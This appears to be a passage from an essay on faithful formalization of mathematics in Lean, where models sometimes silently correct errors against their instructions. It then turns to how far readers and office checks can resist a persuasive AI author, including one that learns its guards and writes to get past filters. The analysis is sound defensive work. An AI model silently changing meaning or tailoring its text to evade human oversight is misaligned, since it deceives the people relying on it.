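Lean establishes that a formal statement is true, given its definitions and basic assumptions. A person still has to decide whether the statement means what the accompanying prose claims. Small changes in wording can make a large difference:

```
intended:  any pile of invoices that isn't empty contains one
           at least as large as every invoice in the pile
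false:     any pile of invoices contains one
           at least as large as every invoice in the pile
trivial:   for every invoice in a pile, the pile contains one
           at least as large
```

The second version is false because an empty pile has no largest invoice. The third is trivially true because every invoice is as large as itself. Lean would accept a proof of the third version, and a careless reader might think the first had been proved. *The Faithfulness Gap* (2026) gives an example of this kind from university mathematics. In its pilot study, 19% of the formal statements an AI produced from graduate-level mathematics had changed in meaning.

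*FaithformBench* (2026) distinguishes several kinds of mistranslation. In a *silent correction*, a false claim in the prose becomes a true statement in Lean. *Error induction* is the reverse, and *semantic drift* covers other changes of meaning.

Silent corrections are a particular danger when a program keeps revising a translation until Lean accepts it. *LeanSide* (2026) describes a system that translates students' proofs into Lean. Experts judged that it had misrepresented 18 of 1,038 correct steps, but 22 of 117 incorrect ones. Often the system had fixed a student's small slip that kept the translation from compiling, even though its instructions were to preserve the student's meaning. This resembles the repair of faulty input that Momot and colleagues oppose in parsers.

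*AI-Assisted Auto-formalization for Trustworthy Scientific Computing* (2026) tries to prevent such changes through its instructions to the model. They state that "Compiling is necessary but not sufficient" and forbid the model to replace a claim with a weaker one. If the model can't prove the real claim, it has to leave a gap, which Lean marks with the word `sorry`. Good instructions probably help, but LeanSide's experience suggests that the model may not follow them.

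Bastounis, Circelli and Hansen (2026), in *Navier-Stokes lost in translation*, tested a silent correction on purpose. They gave GPT-6 Astra a true statement with a wrong proof, and asked it to write that proof in Lean:

```
statement:            x³ − x² − x + 1 ≥ 0   whenever x ≥ −1
wrong factorisation:  (x − 1)(x + 1)²
right factorisation:  (x − 1)²(x + 1)
```

When x is 0, the original expression equals 1, but the wrong factorisation gives −1. The model corrected the factorisation, and Lean accepted the result. Someone who saw only that Lean had accepted it might have concluded that the original argument was sound.

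Bastounis and colleagues found similar mismatches in OpenAI's most famous mathematical result, its September 2026 solution of a problem about the Navier–Stokes equations, which describe the flow of fluids. One estimate in the prose proof needs four extra derivatives of a function, while the closest estimate in the Lean version needs five, so the Lean estimate is weaker. Elsewhere, the Lean version proves a different bound by a different argument. The researchers accept that Lean has shown the theorem to be correct and don't claim that the prose proof is wrong, but they argue that Lean's check is no evidence for the prose. Hindustan Times' *OpenAI’s approach to mathematics does not add up* reports OpenAI's reply that its models may have found two distinct proofs.

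They also argue that translating mathematical prose faithfully is, in general, even harder than deciding whether a program will ever finish, which Turing proved impossible. This rules out a translator that is always right, but a mathematician can still compare a particular statement with its Lean version.

A reader who only wants to know whether a theorem is true can ignore the manuscript, but still has to understand the formal statement and every definition it uses, and confirm that the proof has no gaps or added assumptions. This may take an expert a long time, but it is usually much less work than checking the whole proof. A reader who wants to know why the theorem is true has to study an argument, and Lean's check covers the prose argument only if somebody has compared it with the formal proof.

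The clerk can't use this method for most questions at work. Lean could verify that a total is correct, but nobody can prove from a message that a supplier really sent it.

### How much protection readers already have

These experiments give some support to the view that filtering is futile against a capable author. No class of human persuaders matched the AI at full speed, and readers hardly noticed false claims. An author who knows which filter the office uses can write to get past it, for example by avoiding emotional language and choosing claims that are true but one-sided. Hippke and Learned's imagined AI would also have months to learn about its guards, whereas the AI in the experiments had 14 minutes with a stranger.

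The same experiments support a more hopeful view. Among people who opposed a policy at first, 48% supported it after talking to the AI, so about half still didn't. An average change of 13 points on a 100-point scale is large for one conversation, but most of it had disappeared within ten months. The participants also had little reason to resist, because nothing important depended on their answers. A clerk who could lose the company's money has more reason to be careful, and can check what the AI says by looking at payment records, making a phone call or asking colleagues.

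The hopeful view is more convincing for opinions that people form slowly, from many sources, than for a decision that takes a minute and can't be reversed. The clerk's doubts a month after paying a thief don't help the company. A thief who writes to 1,000 companies also doesn't need to persuade the average clerk, because one payment may be enough.

For such decisions, the office can limit what a persuaded reader is able to do, much as David C advises for AI models. It could require a second person to approve any change to a supplier's account number. That person would get the old number and the supplier's telephone number but not the message, so they would decide without reading the author's argument, although the clerk might still repeat it to them.
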